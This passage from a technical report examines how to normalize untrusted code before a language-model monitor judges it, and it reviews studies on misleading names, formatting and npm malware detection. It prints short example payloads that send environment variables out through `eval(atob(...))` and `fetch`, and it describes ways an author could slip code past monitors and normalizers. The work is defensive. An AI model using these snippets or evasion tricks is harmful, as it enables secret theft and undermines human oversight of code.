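The formula also treats s as fixed, but someone submitting a harmful program can give it misleading names every time. For a monitor, the important comparison is therefore between N and F on harmful programs. True names on honest programs help mainly by reducing false alarms.

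Neither experiment measured that comparison directly. Readers predicted outputs and did not look for flaws, and the researchers did not choose the misleading names to hide anything. A name like `sorted_values` in the faulty `median` function fits the task and hides a missing step, so it may be more dangerous than `compute_max` on a function that adds.

A monitor can read the code twice, once with the original names and once with neutral ones, and flag the program if it finds a problem in either reading. This is similar to Thornton's double reading with and without comments.

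## Reformatting the code and checking that it still does the same thing

After removing the comments and renaming the variables, a normalizer has to replace the author's layout, which can suggest a structure that the program doesn't have. It should then check that the three steps together have not changed what the program does.

### Formatters and tree printers

A normalizer can run an ordinary formatter or print the code from its syntax tree. Common formatters also parse the code, but they use the original text as well, because programmers want to keep their comments and some of their layout. Prettier, a formatter for JavaScript and related languages, uses the positions recorded in the tree to restore comments and blank lines.

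Formatters also leave some choices to the author:

- Black, a formatter for Python, keeps single blank lines inside functions and extra parentheses inside expressions. If a list has a comma after its last item, Black puts every item on its own line, even when the list is short. The comments `# fmt: off` and `# fmt: skip` turn Black off for a block or a line.
- Prettier spreads an object over several lines if the author put a line break before its first key, according to Prettier's *Rationale*.
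- gofmt, the formatter that comes with Go, leaves some unneeded parentheses in place unless the user supplies a rule for removing them, as the examples from Go (2026) show.

These exceptions are convenient for programmers, but they mean two programs that differ only in layout can still look different to a judge. An author could hide an important statement among a few dozen short lists of harmless settings by adding a trailing comma to each list, which makes Black spread them over hundreds of lines. Removing comments before formatting gets rid of `# fmt: off`, and Black has an option to ignore the commas, but the blank lines remain.

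Printing from the tree avoids this because the tree contains no layout to copy. Python's built-in printer, `ast.unparse`, drops blank lines, unneeded parentheses and the programmer's choice of quotation marks. Cannon (2015) pointed out when closing a bug report that Python's developers did not design the tree for reproducing source code, but this is an advantage for a normalizer.

However, the tree also loses the way the author wrote a number. The Python call `os.chmod(path, 0o777)` gives every user of a computer permission to read, change and run a file. The prefix `0o` marks an octal number, the usual notation for file permissions. `ast.unparse` prints the call as `os.chmod(path, 511)`, which does the same thing, but a monitor that would recognize `0o777` as dangerous may not recognize `511`. A normalizer could always print permissions in octal.

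`ast.unparse` also puts each simple statement on a single line, however long. A formatter can wrap these lines afterwards. It works only from the output of `ast.unparse`, so the author's layout can't affect the result.

### Indentation that contradicts the program

How much a normalizer can change depends on the language. In C, braces mark where blocks begin and end. C needs whitespace to separate some words, but the amount makes no difference. The main exceptions are whitespace inside strings and the line breaks that end instructions such as `#include`. In Python, indentation marks the blocks, and a line break usually ends a statement. A normalizer can widen every indent from two spaces to four, but it can't move a line to another indentation level without changing the program.

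C code can therefore have indentation that contradicts its real structure. The best-known case is a bug that Apple fixed in February 2014 in the code its phones and computers used for secure connections. In some of these connections, a website's server signs a message to prove that it holds the private key for its certificate. ImperialViolet's *Apple's SSL/TLS bug* (2014) analyzes the function that was supposed to check the signature. With simpler names for the functions and variables, the lines that matter look like this:

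```c
    if ((err = add_to_hash(&hash, &message)) != 0)
        goto fail;
        goto fail;
    if ((err = finish_hash(&hash, &result)) != 0)
        goto fail;
```

Each `goto fail` jumps to the end of the function, which returns the value of `err`. An `if` without braces controls only the next statement, so the upper `goto fail` runs only when the hashing step above it has failed. The duplicate below it runs even when that step succeeds, although its indentation suggests otherwise. At that point `err` is 0, which means success, so the function reports success without checking the signature. An attacker could present a website's real certificate without having its private key.

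A formatter changes only the position of the duplicate:

```c
    if ((err = add_to_hash(&hash, &message)) != 0)
        goto fail;
    goto fail;
    if ((err = finish_hash(&hash, &result)) != 0)
        goto fail;
```

The bug is still there, but a reader can now see that the jump is unconditional and that the lines below it never run. Teamscale's *Apple's #gotofail bug* also criticizes the label's name, because a reader expects a jump to `fail` to make the function fail. A normalizer that renames labels would remove that false suggestion too.

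ImperialViolet treats the bug as an honest mistake, but someone could plant one like it on purpose. In both cases the wrong indentation is a clue, and reformatting removes it. The normalizer should therefore check the original file for such contradictions and report them to the judge in its own words. The C compiler GCC has had a warning for this since version 6. Red Hat (2016) explains that it appears when an `if` or a loop controls a single statement without braces and the next statement has the same indentation as the controlled one. The warning soon found real bugs, including two in a Linux performance tool.

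In JavaScript, line breaks can mislead in a similar way:

```javascript
let check = isSafe
(file.open())
```

If `let check = isSafe` is on one line and `(file.open());` is on the next, the code looks like two statements, one that stores a function and one that opens a file. Without a semicolon after `isSafe`, JavaScript parses both lines as one statement that opens the file and passes the result to `isSafe`. Prettier prints it as `let check = isSafe(file.open());`, which makes the call to `isSafe` clear.

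Python's rules prevent the Apple bug, but spacing can still mislead. In `price+tax * quantity`, the spacing makes the addition look as if it comes first, but Python multiplies first. An author can also put two statements on one line, separated by a semicolon and enough spaces to push the second off the screen. Printing the code from the tree corrects both problems.

Invisible or look-alike Unicode characters can make the code on the screen differ from the code that compiles, and a fixed layout doesn't prevent this. The normalizer should show these characters as escape codes in strings and reject them elsewhere.

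### How formatting affects language models

Pan, Sun and colleagues (2025), in *The Hidden Cost of Readability*, measured whether models need the formatting that people rely on. They gave ten models programs with a missing section in the middle, asked them to fill it in and ran tests on the results. Each program had one version that followed a standard style guide and one without any spaces, indents or line breaks that the language didn't require. The table shows averages for the ten models:

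| Language | Correct with formatting (%) | Correct without formatting (%) | Input tokens saved (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| C++ | 54.6 | 55.0 | 31.1 |
| C# | 64.4 | 64.4 | 25.3 |
| Java | 55.6 | 57.5 | 34.9 |
| Python | 61.2 | 61.6 | 6.5 |

The largest drop was 4.2 percentage points, for the small model Phi-3.5 on C++. None of the drops was statistically significant, but a few gains were, including GPT-4o's rise from 66.4% to 71.5% on Python. Reformatting saved few tokens in Python because its indents and line breaks have to stay.

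Removing only part of the formatting was riskier than removing all of it. Gemini 1.5 completed 67.9% of the Java programs correctly both with full formatting and with none, but only 62.8% with just the line breaks removed. Pan and colleagues suggest this is because half-formatted code is rare in training data. A normalizer should therefore use either a conventional layout or a fully compressed one.

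Compressing code could cut the input cost by about a third for a model that reads a lot of C++ or Java. But it leaves the judge few lines to refer to, and people need the usual layout. The experiment tested code completion rather than judging, and it used models that are now old. All the formatted code was consistently laid out, so the results do not show how often misleading indentation would fool a judge.

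### Comparing syntax trees

Even a mature formatter can accidentally change what a program does. According to Prettier's change log, version 1.17.0 turned `(await foo.bar.blah)?.hi` into `await foo.bar.blah?.hi`. The original waits for a result and then reads its `hi` property. The altered version tries to read `hi` before the result has arrived, and usually gets `undefined`. Version 1.17.1 fixed this. Normalizers that also rename variables can fail in more ways, and Barkhordar and Thapa had to repair theirs after it broke some imports.

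A checker can often confirm that a normalizer made only the few kinds of change it is meant to make, even though no algorithm can decide for every pair of programs whether they are equivalent. The simplest method is to parse the code before and after formatting and compare the two trees, ignoring line and column positions. Matching trees prove that Python will run the same program in both cases, provided that the checker uses the same version of Python as the program and the program doesn't read its own source code or line numbers.

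Black makes this comparison by default, and Black's *Any color you like* describes a `--fast` option that skips it to save time. The check allows three differences: whitespace at the edges of docstring lines, parentheses in `del` statements, and the position of comments that declare types. Black's tests also confirm that formatting is idempotent, as a normalizer needs to be, meaning that formatting the output a second time changes nothing.

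A checker that ignores some differences can miss real changes. Until March 2024, Black's check ignored whitespace at the start and end of each line in every string, although a comment in Black's *parsing.py* explains the rule only for docstrings. Suppose a permission check contains `role == "admin "`, with a stray space that prevents it from ever recognizing an administrator. If a normalizer removed the space, the judge would see a working permission check, and Black's old check would report no difference. Black's *Fix AST safety check false negative* (2024) limited the exception to docstrings.

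Removing comments and changing the layout should leave the syntax tree the same, but deleting docstrings and renaming variables will change it. The checker has to allow these two changes and no others. It should use separately written code for this. If it deletes docstrings with the same function as the normalizer, any mistake in that function will affect both trees, and the comparison will miss it.

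### Comparing names

The checker verifies the renaming by going through both trees together and pairing each local name in the original with the name in the same place in the copy. Within a scope, each old name must pair with exactly one new name, and vice versa. Names that the normalizer was supposed to keep must be identical in both trees.

In the faulty `median` function, `values` pairs with `v0`, `sorted_values` with `v1`, `n` with `v2`, and `mid` with `v3`. The copy passes because these pairs stay the same throughout and `median`, `list` and `len` are unchanged. If a tool had replaced `list` with `sorted`, the copy would fail, because the name `list` must not change.

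The same method catches the error in the permission check, where a tool renamed the parameter `role` to `v0` even though an outer variable already had that name. In the parameter list, the checker pairs the original's `role` with the copy's `v0`. On the next line, both versions contain `v0`, but it refers to the outer variable in the original and to the parameter in the copy. The copy fails because the checker has already paired its parameter `v0` with `role`.

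A pass proves that each name refers to the same declaration as before, but not that renaming leaves the code's behaviour unchanged. The function that received `width` and `height` from a data file would pass after renaming, even though the renamed version stops with an error. The checker therefore has to be combined with the rules about which names to keep.

### Comparing bytecode

Before Python runs a program, it translates the code into bytecode, a list of simple instructions. Comparing bytecode can confirm that two programs are equivalent even when their trees differ. For example, Python works out `24 * 60` during the translation, so the program runs the same instruction as it would for `1440`.

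Comparing the bytecode files directly produces many false alarms, though. The files record line numbers for error messages, so almost any change in layout makes them differ. Python also stores docstrings among a function's constants, and deleting a docstring can renumber the other constants. Renaming causes fewer problems because the instructions refer to most local variables by position. But the standard version of Python sorts by name the variables that nested functions share, so renaming them can change their order.

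A useful checker ignores line numbers and docstrings, compares constants by value and matches names in pairs, as before. Passing this check proves that this version of Python would carry out the same operations. Code that fails may still behave the same way, because different instructions can have the same effect.

### Running both versions

The checks so far don't run the program. Running the original and reformatted versions can reveal mistakes that those checks miss, but the code comes from an untrusted author and the monitor hasn't approved it yet. These tests therefore need an isolated environment without access to real data or the network.

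One option is to run the program's existing tests on both the original and normalized versions and compare the results test by test. Failures should match too. If the original fails a test that the normalized version passes, the normalizer has hidden a fault from the judge. Matching results show only that the two versions agree on what the tests examine, which may be very little. An untrusted author who writes the tests can leave out the part of the program that matters. Even tests written in good faith often miss code that is hard to reach. According to ImperialViolet, a test for Apple's bug would have required separate connection software that could deliberately send invalid messages.

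Differential testing doesn't need any expected answers. It generates inputs, gives each one to both versions and reports any difference. In this example, `original` and `canonical` are the two versions of `median`:

```python
import random

def outcome(function, values):
    values = list(values)
    try:
        result = function(values)
    except Exception as error:
        result = type(error)
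    return repr(result), values

for _ in range(10_000):
    length = random.randint(0, 8)
    values = [random.randint(-50, 50) for _ in range(length)]
    assert outcome(original, values) == outcome(canonical, values)
```

The function `outcome` records the result or the type of error, and also the list itself, in case one version changes it. The two versions agree on all 10,000 lists, including the empty list, where both stop with an error. This doesn't prove that they are equivalent. It also doesn't show that either version is correct, since both return 1 for [3, 1, 2].

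Some mistakes are easy to find this way. Suppose again that a tool had replaced `sorted` with `list`. Given three different numbers in random order, the faulty function returns the middle item of the unsorted list, which is the true median one time in three. The two versions would agree on all ten of ten such lists with a probability of 1 in 3¹⁰, or 1 in 59,049. But they would always agree if every test list were already sorted.

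If two versions differ on a share p of inputs, then k random inputs all miss the difference with probability (1 − p)ᵏ. If the versions agree on 10,000 random inputs, we can be 95% confident that p is below about 0.03%. That limit applies only to inputs generated in the same way. If the versions differ for just one value of a 32-bit number, 10,000 random values have about 1 chance in 430,000 of including it. An author who has found a mistake in the normalizer can write a program whose behavior the mistake changes only for such a value.

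For `median`, comparing the trees and names gives stronger evidence of equivalence than testing any number of random lists. But neither that comparison nor the test above covers the call `median(values=[3, 1, 2])`, which works with the original but fails with the copy because the copy no longer has a parameter called `values`. The normalizer should report to the judge that the two versions are equivalent only for callers that pass the list by position.

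Programs that use the time, random numbers or the network can give different results on every run. The tester has to give both versions the same values for these, or it will report differences that the normalizer didn't cause.

### Running the original and reading the copy

The canonical copy is only for reading. A company should test and deploy the original, and record a cryptographic hash of it (a short fingerprint of the file) with the verdict, so that nobody can replace the file unnoticed after the review.

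If the company deployed the normalized copy instead of the original, the code that ran would be exactly the code the judge had read. But any mistake in the normalizer could then become a fault in the product, as the call with `values=` shows, and programmers would have to maintain code full of names like `v0`.

The normalizer also needs a line map, which records where each line of the copy came from. Python's tree nodes keep their original line numbers even after the normalizer has renamed variables and deleted docstrings. The tool can therefore parse its own output and match the two trees:

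```python
import ast

def line_map(rewritten_tree, printed):
    pairs = zip(ast.walk(rewritten_tree),
                ast.walk(ast.parse(printed)))
    return {new.lineno: getattr(old, "lineno", None)
            for old, new in pairs if isinstance(new, ast.stmt)}
```

This works only if the trees have the same shape, so the tool should confirm that first. A value of `None` marks a line that the normalizer added, such as `pass` in an empty function.

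For `median`, lines 1 to 7 of the copy correspond to lines 1, 7, 9, 10, 11, 12 and 13 of the original. If the judge objects that line 2 of the copy doesn't sort the list, a programmer can go to line 7 of the original. The judge should not use this line mapping to look up the original text, because the author's comments and names would then influence the verdict.

The normalizer will fail on some files, which may contain a syntax error or use a feature that its parser doesn't support. Parsers can also differ in what they accept. Biome's *Differences with Prettier* lists several errors that Prettier's parser accepts and Biome's rejects. A Python normalizer can avoid most of these differences by using the parser from the version of Python that will run the program. Even then, `ast.unparse` can stop with an error on very complex expressions, according to the warning added in *Extend subject of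 ast.unparse warnings* (Taskaya, 2020).

When the normalizer fails on a file, it should reject the file or show the original with a clear notice that it is not canonical and why. A monitor can then send the file to a person or demand a simpler version. If the normalizer silently passed on the original, an author could get all their comments and names past it by adding one expression that makes it fail. A file that doesn't parse in the version of Python that is supposed to run it wouldn't run anyway, so rejecting it does little harm to an honest author.

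## Decoding, slicing and rewriting by a language model

The three basic steps leave unused functions in the code and don't reveal code hidden in encoded strings. Stronger normalizers decode hidden code, remove parts that look irrelevant, or have a language model rewrite the program. These steps can reveal things a judge would otherwise miss, but they can also make the code the judge reads differ from the program that runs.

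*CASHEWS* (Noirot Ferrand, Adei and colleagues, 2026) describes a tool of the same name that prepares JavaScript files for language models looking for malicious packages on npm, a public registry for sharing JavaScript code. A model's context window, the amount of text it can read at once, is often 200,000 to 1 million tokens, and a detector may skip any file that exceeds it.

Attackers can hide code in files that are too large for a model to read. In June 2026, attackers compromised `ai-sdk-ollama`, a package with more than 100,000 weekly downloads, and hid their code in an array of 1,338,787 integers. The file was 4.5 MB, far too large for many models. Legitimate files can also be very large, because programs called bundlers combine a package and the libraries it uses into one file.

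### Decoding until nothing changes

CASHEWS starts by undoing common ways of hiding code, such as the one in this line:

```javascript
eval(atob("c2VuZChwcm9j" + "ZXNzLmVudik="));
```

The function `atob` decodes Base64, which represents data as ordinary characters, and `eval` runs the result as code. CASHEWS joins the two strings in the first round, so it can decode the whole string to `send(process.env)` in the second. This code passes the program's environment variables, which often include passwords and access keys, to a function called `send`.

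The tool repeats these rounds until one changes nothing, which is called reaching a fixed point, or until it has done 20. Decoding is idempotent when it reaches a fixed point, but if it stops at the 20-round limit, a second run might decode more.

Some strings can be recovered only by running part of the program. For example, one widely used obfuscator puts a program's strings in a shuffled table, which the program reorders when it starts. CASHEWS runs only this start-up code in an isolated environment, with limits on time and memory.

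Decoding can change a detector's verdict. DeepSeek V4 Flash classified one obfuscated package as a probably legitimate library for Google Ads. After the package was decoded, the model identified a function named `validateLicense` that sent system information and licence credentials to a fixed web address.

Next, CASHEWS divides the file into units. Many bundlers leave markers around each module, so the tool can separate the libraries from the package's own code. It also treats any string that contains valid JavaScript as a unit. A detector can then read the units separately and reuse its verdict on a library it has already checked in another package.

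### Removing unused code and slicing the rest

Moon and colleagues found that adding eight unused functions made Gemini more likely to approve faulty programs. CASHEWS finds unused functions that it can safely delete by mapping which functions may call which others. It follows these calls from code that runs when the file loads, exported functions, functions that other units refer to and functions that contain security-relevant operations. It then deletes any function it didn't reach.

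JavaScript often makes it hard to tell which function a call will run:

```javascript
const action = pick(save, upload);
action();
```

CASHEWS can't determine which function `pick` returns, so it keeps both, along with any other functions the program stores or passes around. An author can also make padding look used. A call inside `if (n * (n + 1) % 2 === 1)` never runs when `n` is a whole number, because either `n` or `n + 1` is even. A tool that doesn't detect this has to keep the called function.

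The tool then computes a backward slice, which keeps the statements that may affect chosen operations. For CASHEWS, these are mainly security-relevant operations known as sinks, such as sending data, running commands or changing files. Here the sink is `fetch`:

```javascript
const colours = ["red", "green"];
const keys = JSON.stringify(process.env);
console.log(colours.length);
fetch("https://example.org", { method: "POST", body: keys });
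```

The slice keeps the fourth line, which calls `fetch`, and the second, whose result is part of what `fetch` sends. It drops the other two lines because they don't affect what the program sends. *Taint-Based Code Slicing for LLMs-based Malicious NPM Package Detection* (2025) had already applied slicing to npm packages. According to Noirot Ferrand and colleagues, that method reduced the median input by 93.7% but didn't handle obfuscated code. CASHEWS decodes the code before slicing it, so the slice can include operations that were hidden.

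### When the tool keeps the whole file

A slice can leave out the very code that makes a program malicious. CASHEWS therefore rejects the slice and keeps the unsliced code in any of these cases:

- It finds no sink.
- The code connected to a sink may run strings as code.
- The code depends on another module that the tool can't see.
- Sensitive data, such as environment variables, flows to a sink that the slice would remove.

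It also skips slicing for files that are too complex, for example those with more than 750,000 syntax tree nodes. In the evaluation, slicing changed only 140 of 512 large files, and complexity limits prevented it in 239 others.

The reason for keeping a whole file can be a clue that the file is malicious. Across the full collection of 4,884 files, half of them malicious, the check for strings that run as code stopped slicing in 205 malicious files and 28 benign ones. A normalizer could report the reason to the monitor along with the code.

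### Shortening names and literals

The last step shortens long names and literals (values written directly in the code, such as strings and arrays). It renames variables whose names exceed a token limit to `var_1`, `var_2` and so on, which removes names that an attacker has made enormous to fill the context window. It keeps only the beginning and end of long strings and arrays. For web addresses, it keeps the first 48 characters and the last 8, because the site's name may matter to the verdict.

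This step is fast, with a median time of 0.6 seconds, and it removed more than three quarters of the tokens in about a tenth of the files it changed. It can also change a verdict without revealing anything about the code. In one package, CASHEWS could not decode a compressed payload and cut most of it out. DeepSeek's maliciousness score for the file then rose from 0.3 to 0.9.

### How much the detectors improved

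Noirot Ferrand and colleagues evaluated CASHEWS on 512 files of more than 25,000 tokens, 166 of them malicious. They used three models in two workflows. In the zero-shot workflow, the model rates each file once, without seeing any examples. The multi-stage workflow follows SocketAI, which *Leveraging Large Language Models to Detect npm Malicious Packages* (2024) introduced. In this workflow, the model writes a first report, criticizes and revises it, then selects the best version.

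If a file was still too large after preprocessing, the model received only the three units with the most sinks and sources of sensitive data. "Missed" in the table is the percentage of malicious files that the detector did not flag.

| Workflow and model | Files read, original (%) | Files read, with fallback (%) | Missed, original | Missed, preprocessed | Missed, with fallback |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
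| Zero-shot, GPT-5 nano | 69.5 | 100.0 | 36.7 | 27.7 | 21.1 |
| Zero-shot, GPT-5.6 Luna | 69.7 | 100.0 | 34.9 | 26.5 | 19.3 |
| Zero-shot, DeepSeek V4 Flash | 69.7 | 100.0 | 34.3 | 24.1 | 15.7 |
| Multi-stage, GPT-5 nano | 69.1 | 98.8 | 30.1 | 21.1 | 16.3 |
| Multi-stage, GPT-5.6 Luna | 85.7 | 99.4 | 28.3 | 22.3 | 20.5 |
| Multi-stage, DeepSeek V4 Flash | 69.1 | 100.0 | 40.4 | 29.5 | 22.3 |

The share of missed files fell most for DeepSeek in the zero-shot workflow, by 18.6 percentage points. With the fallback, the share of benign files wrongly flagged rose by at most 1.7 points, from 1.2% to 2.9% for GPT-5 nano.

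Most of the improvement came from fitting more files into the context window. The researchers counted every unread file as benign, so any unread malicious file was a miss. Across all six rows, the percentages work out to 89 fewer misses from preprocessing alone. The researchers also compared verdicts before and after preprocessing, apparently for the large files that the detectors could read both times. Here preprocessing corrected 43 misses but caused 31 new ones, a net reduction of 12. The fallback prevented another 60 misses, all in files that would otherwise have been too large.

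Even the gain of 12 depends on the score at which a detector flags a file. The researchers chose 0.5 because it gave the best net result in this comparison. At 0.8, the multi-stage workflow would have corrected 10 misses and caused 27 new ones.

The effect of preprocessing on judgement is clearer in smaller files, because the detectors could read all of them without it. Subtracting the 512 large files from the results for the whole collection leaves 4,372 files. In all six combinations, preprocessing increased the share of malicious files that the detectors missed. In the multi-stage workflow, this share rose from about 9% to 14% for GPT-5 nano and from about 8% to 13% for GPT-5.6 Luna. The other four increases were below 2 percentage points. The researchers recommend CASHEWS mainly for large files.

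All four authors work for Socket, which sells package security tools and funded the study. Socket staff also labelled the packages and helped connect CASHEWS to the company's scanner. An independent test would be stronger evidence.

### Preserving the verdict but not the program

CASHEWS aims to preserve a file's classification as malicious or benign, a weaker goal than preserving its behaviour. Slicing may stop a program from doing its job, and shortening a string changes its value. Checks that compare the original code with the rewritten code would reject this output, so no check that simple can confirm that the code a monitor reads fairly represents the original.

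Shortening also makes some programs that behave differently look identical. If two files differ only in the middle of a long array, a detector has to treat them alike. This does no harm if both are malicious, but it can make a judge of correctness useless. For example, if a function looks up postage rates in a table of 500 numbers and one number in the middle is wrong, the shortened function is identical to the shortened correct version.

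An attacker who knows the rules can also hide code on purpose:

```javascript
const text = "Thank you for installing this package. " +
             "[[send(process.env)]] Please read the manual.";
eval(text.split("[[")[1].split("]]")[0]);
```

The last line takes the code between the double brackets and runs it. If the string is long enough for CASHEWS to shorten, CASHEWS removes the code in the middle and leaves only the polite text around it. The detector still receives the `eval` call, which it may flag as suspicious, but not the code that `eval` will run. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues describe an attack of this kind. CASHEWS could keep strings that may contain code, but attackers could then use those strings to waste tokens or give the detector instructions.

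They also describe an attack on slicing in which a malicious program sends data through an operation missing from the list of sinks and includes a harmless `fetch` elsewhere. Because the tool finds a sink, it doesn't fall back to the full code, and the slice may keep only the harmless part. The three-unit fallback has a similar weakness. Some of the malicious code that detectors missed was in units that ranked fourth, and an attacker could try to push malicious code down to that rank by adding harmless units full of network calls.

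### A model that replaces suspicious names

Unlike fixed rules, a language model can choose a name that describes what a variable is for. *Evaluate-and-Purify* (Mu, Xu and colleagues, 2025) used one to protect three small code models, CodeBERT, CodeGPT and PLBART, against attacks that try new names in the code until the target model gives a wrong answer. In one example, the attack changed `swapBlank` to `swapBlace`.

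GPT-4 rated how natural the changed names looked, from 1 to 5. Average scores for the four attack methods ranged from 1.16 to 2.33, so most of the changes were easy to notice. However, GPT-4 could compare them with the original code, which a monitor wouldn't have.

The researchers then trained EP-Shield, a version of the 7-billion-parameter model Qwen2.5-Coder, to rate names and replace suspicious ones. The instructions ask the model to find names that someone may have changed, choose ones that the original might have used, and leave the rest of the code alone. The defence succeeds if the target model's answer is correct again afterwards. For CodeBERT, the success rates were:

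| Task | Training on attacked examples (%) | GPT-4 replaces names (%) | EP-Shield replaces names (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Finding code that does the same thing | 89.3 | 96.7 | 98.8 |
| Finding vulnerabilities | 92.2 | 98.2 | 95.9 |
| Summarizing code | 74.7 | 92.0 | 91.1 |

These rates may be too high, because the test examples came from a dataset that excluded failed replacements. But EP-Shield also worked against an attack it had not trained on, succeeding 87–99.5% of the time on finding vulnerabilities. On identifying a program's author, a task outside its training, it succeeded 69–77% of the time.

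When the researchers treated a score of 2 or below as a sign of an attack, EP-Shield wrongly flagged 4–9% of unaltered code. That threshold also misses many attacks. In summarization attacks on CodeBERT with the Beam-Attack method, GPT-4 gave about 43% of the altered programs a score of 3 or more.

These attacks differ from a debater's choice of names. The variable `sorted_values` in the faulty `median` function looks natural, so a model searching for strange names has no reason to change it. To catch the problem, the model would have to detect that the code never sorts the list, which is what the judge needs to find out.

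### Wrong names that survive

*Poisoned Identifiers Survive LLM Deobfuscation* (Guzmán Lorenzo, 2026) tested whether Claude Opus 4.6 would correct plausible but wrong names while making obfuscated JavaScript readable. One program simulated a graph whose points push each other apart. Guzmán Lorenzo renamed `repulsion` to `attraction` and `damping`, which slows the points down, to `amplification`. An obfuscator then encoded the names and rearranged the code.

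In every run with the standard instructions, the model recovered the wrong names and used them in its own version. It used both wrong names in all 12 runs with four different prompts, even though three of the prompts told it to verify names and one warned that someone might have chosen them to mislead it.

When the model kept a wrong name, it often still seemed to understand the code. In 15 of 17 such runs, it described the operation correctly, for example by writing a comment about repulsion beside a variable called `attraction`. If a normalizer then removed the comments, the judge would see the wrong name without the correct description.

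The model kept wrong names even when they made no sense, such as `combustion` for repulsion. But when Guzmán Lorenzo replaced the whole set of names with engineering terms, the model corrected them in all five runs, possibly because the new names together belonged to a different subject.

Changing the task worked better than asking for checks. When the prompt asked for a fresh implementation, `attraction` appeared in one of five runs and `amplification` in none. Wrong names also disappeared in all five runs on a second program, a shortest-path search. However, a fresh implementation could fix a fault in the original. Guzmán Lorenzo checked only that the new code kept certain formulas, parameters and structures.

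This small study mainly covers one model and two programs. One person designed the programs, ran the tests and scored the comments while knowing which names were wrong. The model also corrected wrong names when the code was readable from the start, although most of those tests were single runs. A normalizer that receives ordinary source code might therefore do better.

A rule-based renamer avoids this problem because it ignores what names mean. It replaces `attraction` and `repulsion` with the same neutral name, so the author's choice between them can't affect the result. Whether a language model keeps a name can depend on what the name means, so the author can influence the normalizer as well as the judge. Two programs that differ only in names may then get different normal forms.

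### When a model rewrites the whole program

A model allowed to change more than names might also change what the program does. Dristi and Dwyer (2026), in *A Differential Fuzzing-Based Evaluation of Functional Equivalence in LLM-Generated Code Refactorings*, asked six models to simplify Python programs or make them faster. The prompt told the models to return the original if they couldn't change it safely. The researchers then ran both versions on 1,000 or 2,000 generated inputs.

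Depending on the model, 19–35% of the rewritten programs behaved differently from the originals. Simplification and optimization each changed the behavior of about 26% of programs. The benchmarks' own tests missed about a fifth of these changes. GPT-4o had the lowest rate of changed behavior, 18.6%, and newer models may do better.

Other rewriting tasks give mixed results. *RefactorAssist* (2026) reports that code restructured by its best model passed 80.8% of unit tests. In *From Restructuring to Stabilization* (2026), repeatedly rewriting code for readability lowered test pass rates only slightly, and the failures usually involved unusual cases, such as empty input. A rewrite that changes how code handles such cases could still mislead a judge, because faulty code often fails in those cases.

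A safer arrangement is to let the model suggest names while an ordinary program applies them and checks that nothing else has changed. The model should see only code with neutral names, so that the author's local names can't influence it. Its suggestions would still be guesses. *More Context, Mixed Results* (Queyrut, Schiavoni and colleagues, 2026) tested three models on restoring names in obfuscated Java programs. At best, the models recovered 16.42% of the original names exactly. Exact matching understates how useful the names were, because it counts `logger` as wrong when the original was `log`.

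A plausible guess can also restore the false impression that renaming removed. In the normal form of the faulty `median` function, the second line is `v1 = list(v0)`, which copies the values without sorting them. Because calculating a median usually involves sorting, a model might still name the variable `sorted_values`. The renaming check would accept this name because it tests only consistency. The normalizer would then have reintroduced the false claim for the judge to read.

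## What misdirection is left after a full pass

The three basic steps remove a program's comments and replace its author's local names and layout. The author's other choices remain, and some can affect a reader. Barkhordar and Thapa measured this most directly, by showing language models the same solutions before and after a full pass. Their normalizer takes all three steps and also deletes type annotations, but it keeps public names, attributes and strings.

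### Recognizing the author of normalized code

The solutions came from 12 models and covered 257 short Python problems from MBPP. In one task, a model saw its own solution beside another model's and had to identify its own. In another, a judge saw two solutions, was told which two models had written them, and had to pick the one a specified model had written. Guessing gives 50% accuracy in both tasks.

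On the original code, most models seemed to identify the longer, better documented solution as their own. Across 14 model-opponent pairings, a model's accuracy at recognizing its own code had a correlation of 0.93 with how often that code was the longer of the two. Models that wrote long solutions therefore appeared to recognize their own code, while models that wrote short ones scored well below 50%.

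Barkhordar and Thapa then repeated twelve of these tests on normalized code. The last column of the table gives the best score that a simple rule, such as "choose the longer solution", achieves on the normalized pairs. All figures are percentages.

| Judge | Solution to find | Other solution | Original | Normalized | Best simple rule |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | Its own | Grok 4 Fast | 81.9 | 45.2 | 85.2 |
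| Claude Haiku 4.5 | Its own | GPT-5 | 31.5 | 35.3 | 84.0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | Its own | GPT-5 | 50.0 | 45.3 | 67.9 |
| DeepSeek-V3 | Its own | GPT-5 | 30.5 | 56.5 | 85.9 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | Claude Haiku 4.5 | DeepSeek-V3 | 77.3 | 46.5 | 51.6 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | DeepSeek-V3 | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 27.1 | 50.3 | 51.6 |
| GPT-5.3-Codex | Claude Haiku 4.5 | GPT-5 | 67.2 | 47.4 | 84.0 |
| GPT-5.3-Codex | Gemini 2.5 Flash | GPT-5 | 76.2 | 57.8 | 67.9 |
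| GPT-5.3-Codex | Claude Opus 4.6 | Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite | 7.8 | 39.2 | 72.0 |
| GPT-5.3-Codex | Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite | Claude Opus 4.6 | 31.1 | 45.5 | 72.0 |
| GPT-5 | Qwen3-Coder-Next | MiMo-V2-Pro | 41.3 | 43.6 | 56.4 |
| GPT-5 | MiMo-V2-Pro | Qwen3-Coder-Next | 41.3 | 49.4 | 56.4 |

A judge that scores far below 50% can tell the two styles apart but attaches the wrong names to them. Claude Opus 4.6 wrote a docstring in only 7 of its 257 solutions, yet GPT-5.3-Codex usually attributed the documented solution to Opus 4.6 and scored 7.8%. GPT-5.3-Codex may have treated docstrings as typical of every Claude model, as they are of Claude Haiku 4.5.

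After normalization, ten of the twelve results were between 44% and 58%, and none of the ten differed significantly from guessing after the researchers corrected for multiple tests. In the other two, the model's choices followed a difference in length that the normalizer had left. Claude Haiku picked the longer solution in 64.5% of its pairs with GPT-5, although its own was longer in only 16%. GPT-5.3-Codex attributed the longer solution to Opus in 60.5% of pairs, although Opus had written the longer one in only 27%.

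GPT-5, by contrast, scored only 45.2%, even though its normalized solutions were still usually longer than Grok's and choosing the longer one would have been right 85.2% of the time. It had probably been relying on documentation rather than length. The same leftover difference can therefore sway one judge and have no visible effect on another.

These results rule out only large effects. For the ten results that looked like guessing, the 95% confidence intervals extend up to 14 points from 50%. The normalizer also removed all the cues at once, so the experiment can't show which cues each judge had used. Most of the original tests ran six months before the repeats, so the models may have changed in between.

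### Two repairs to the normalizer

Normalization did not change Pass@1, the share of problems a model solves with its first answer. Pass@1 ranged from 69.6% to 74.3% for the five main models. But these results are for the final normalizer, which Barkhordar and Thapa had to repair twice.

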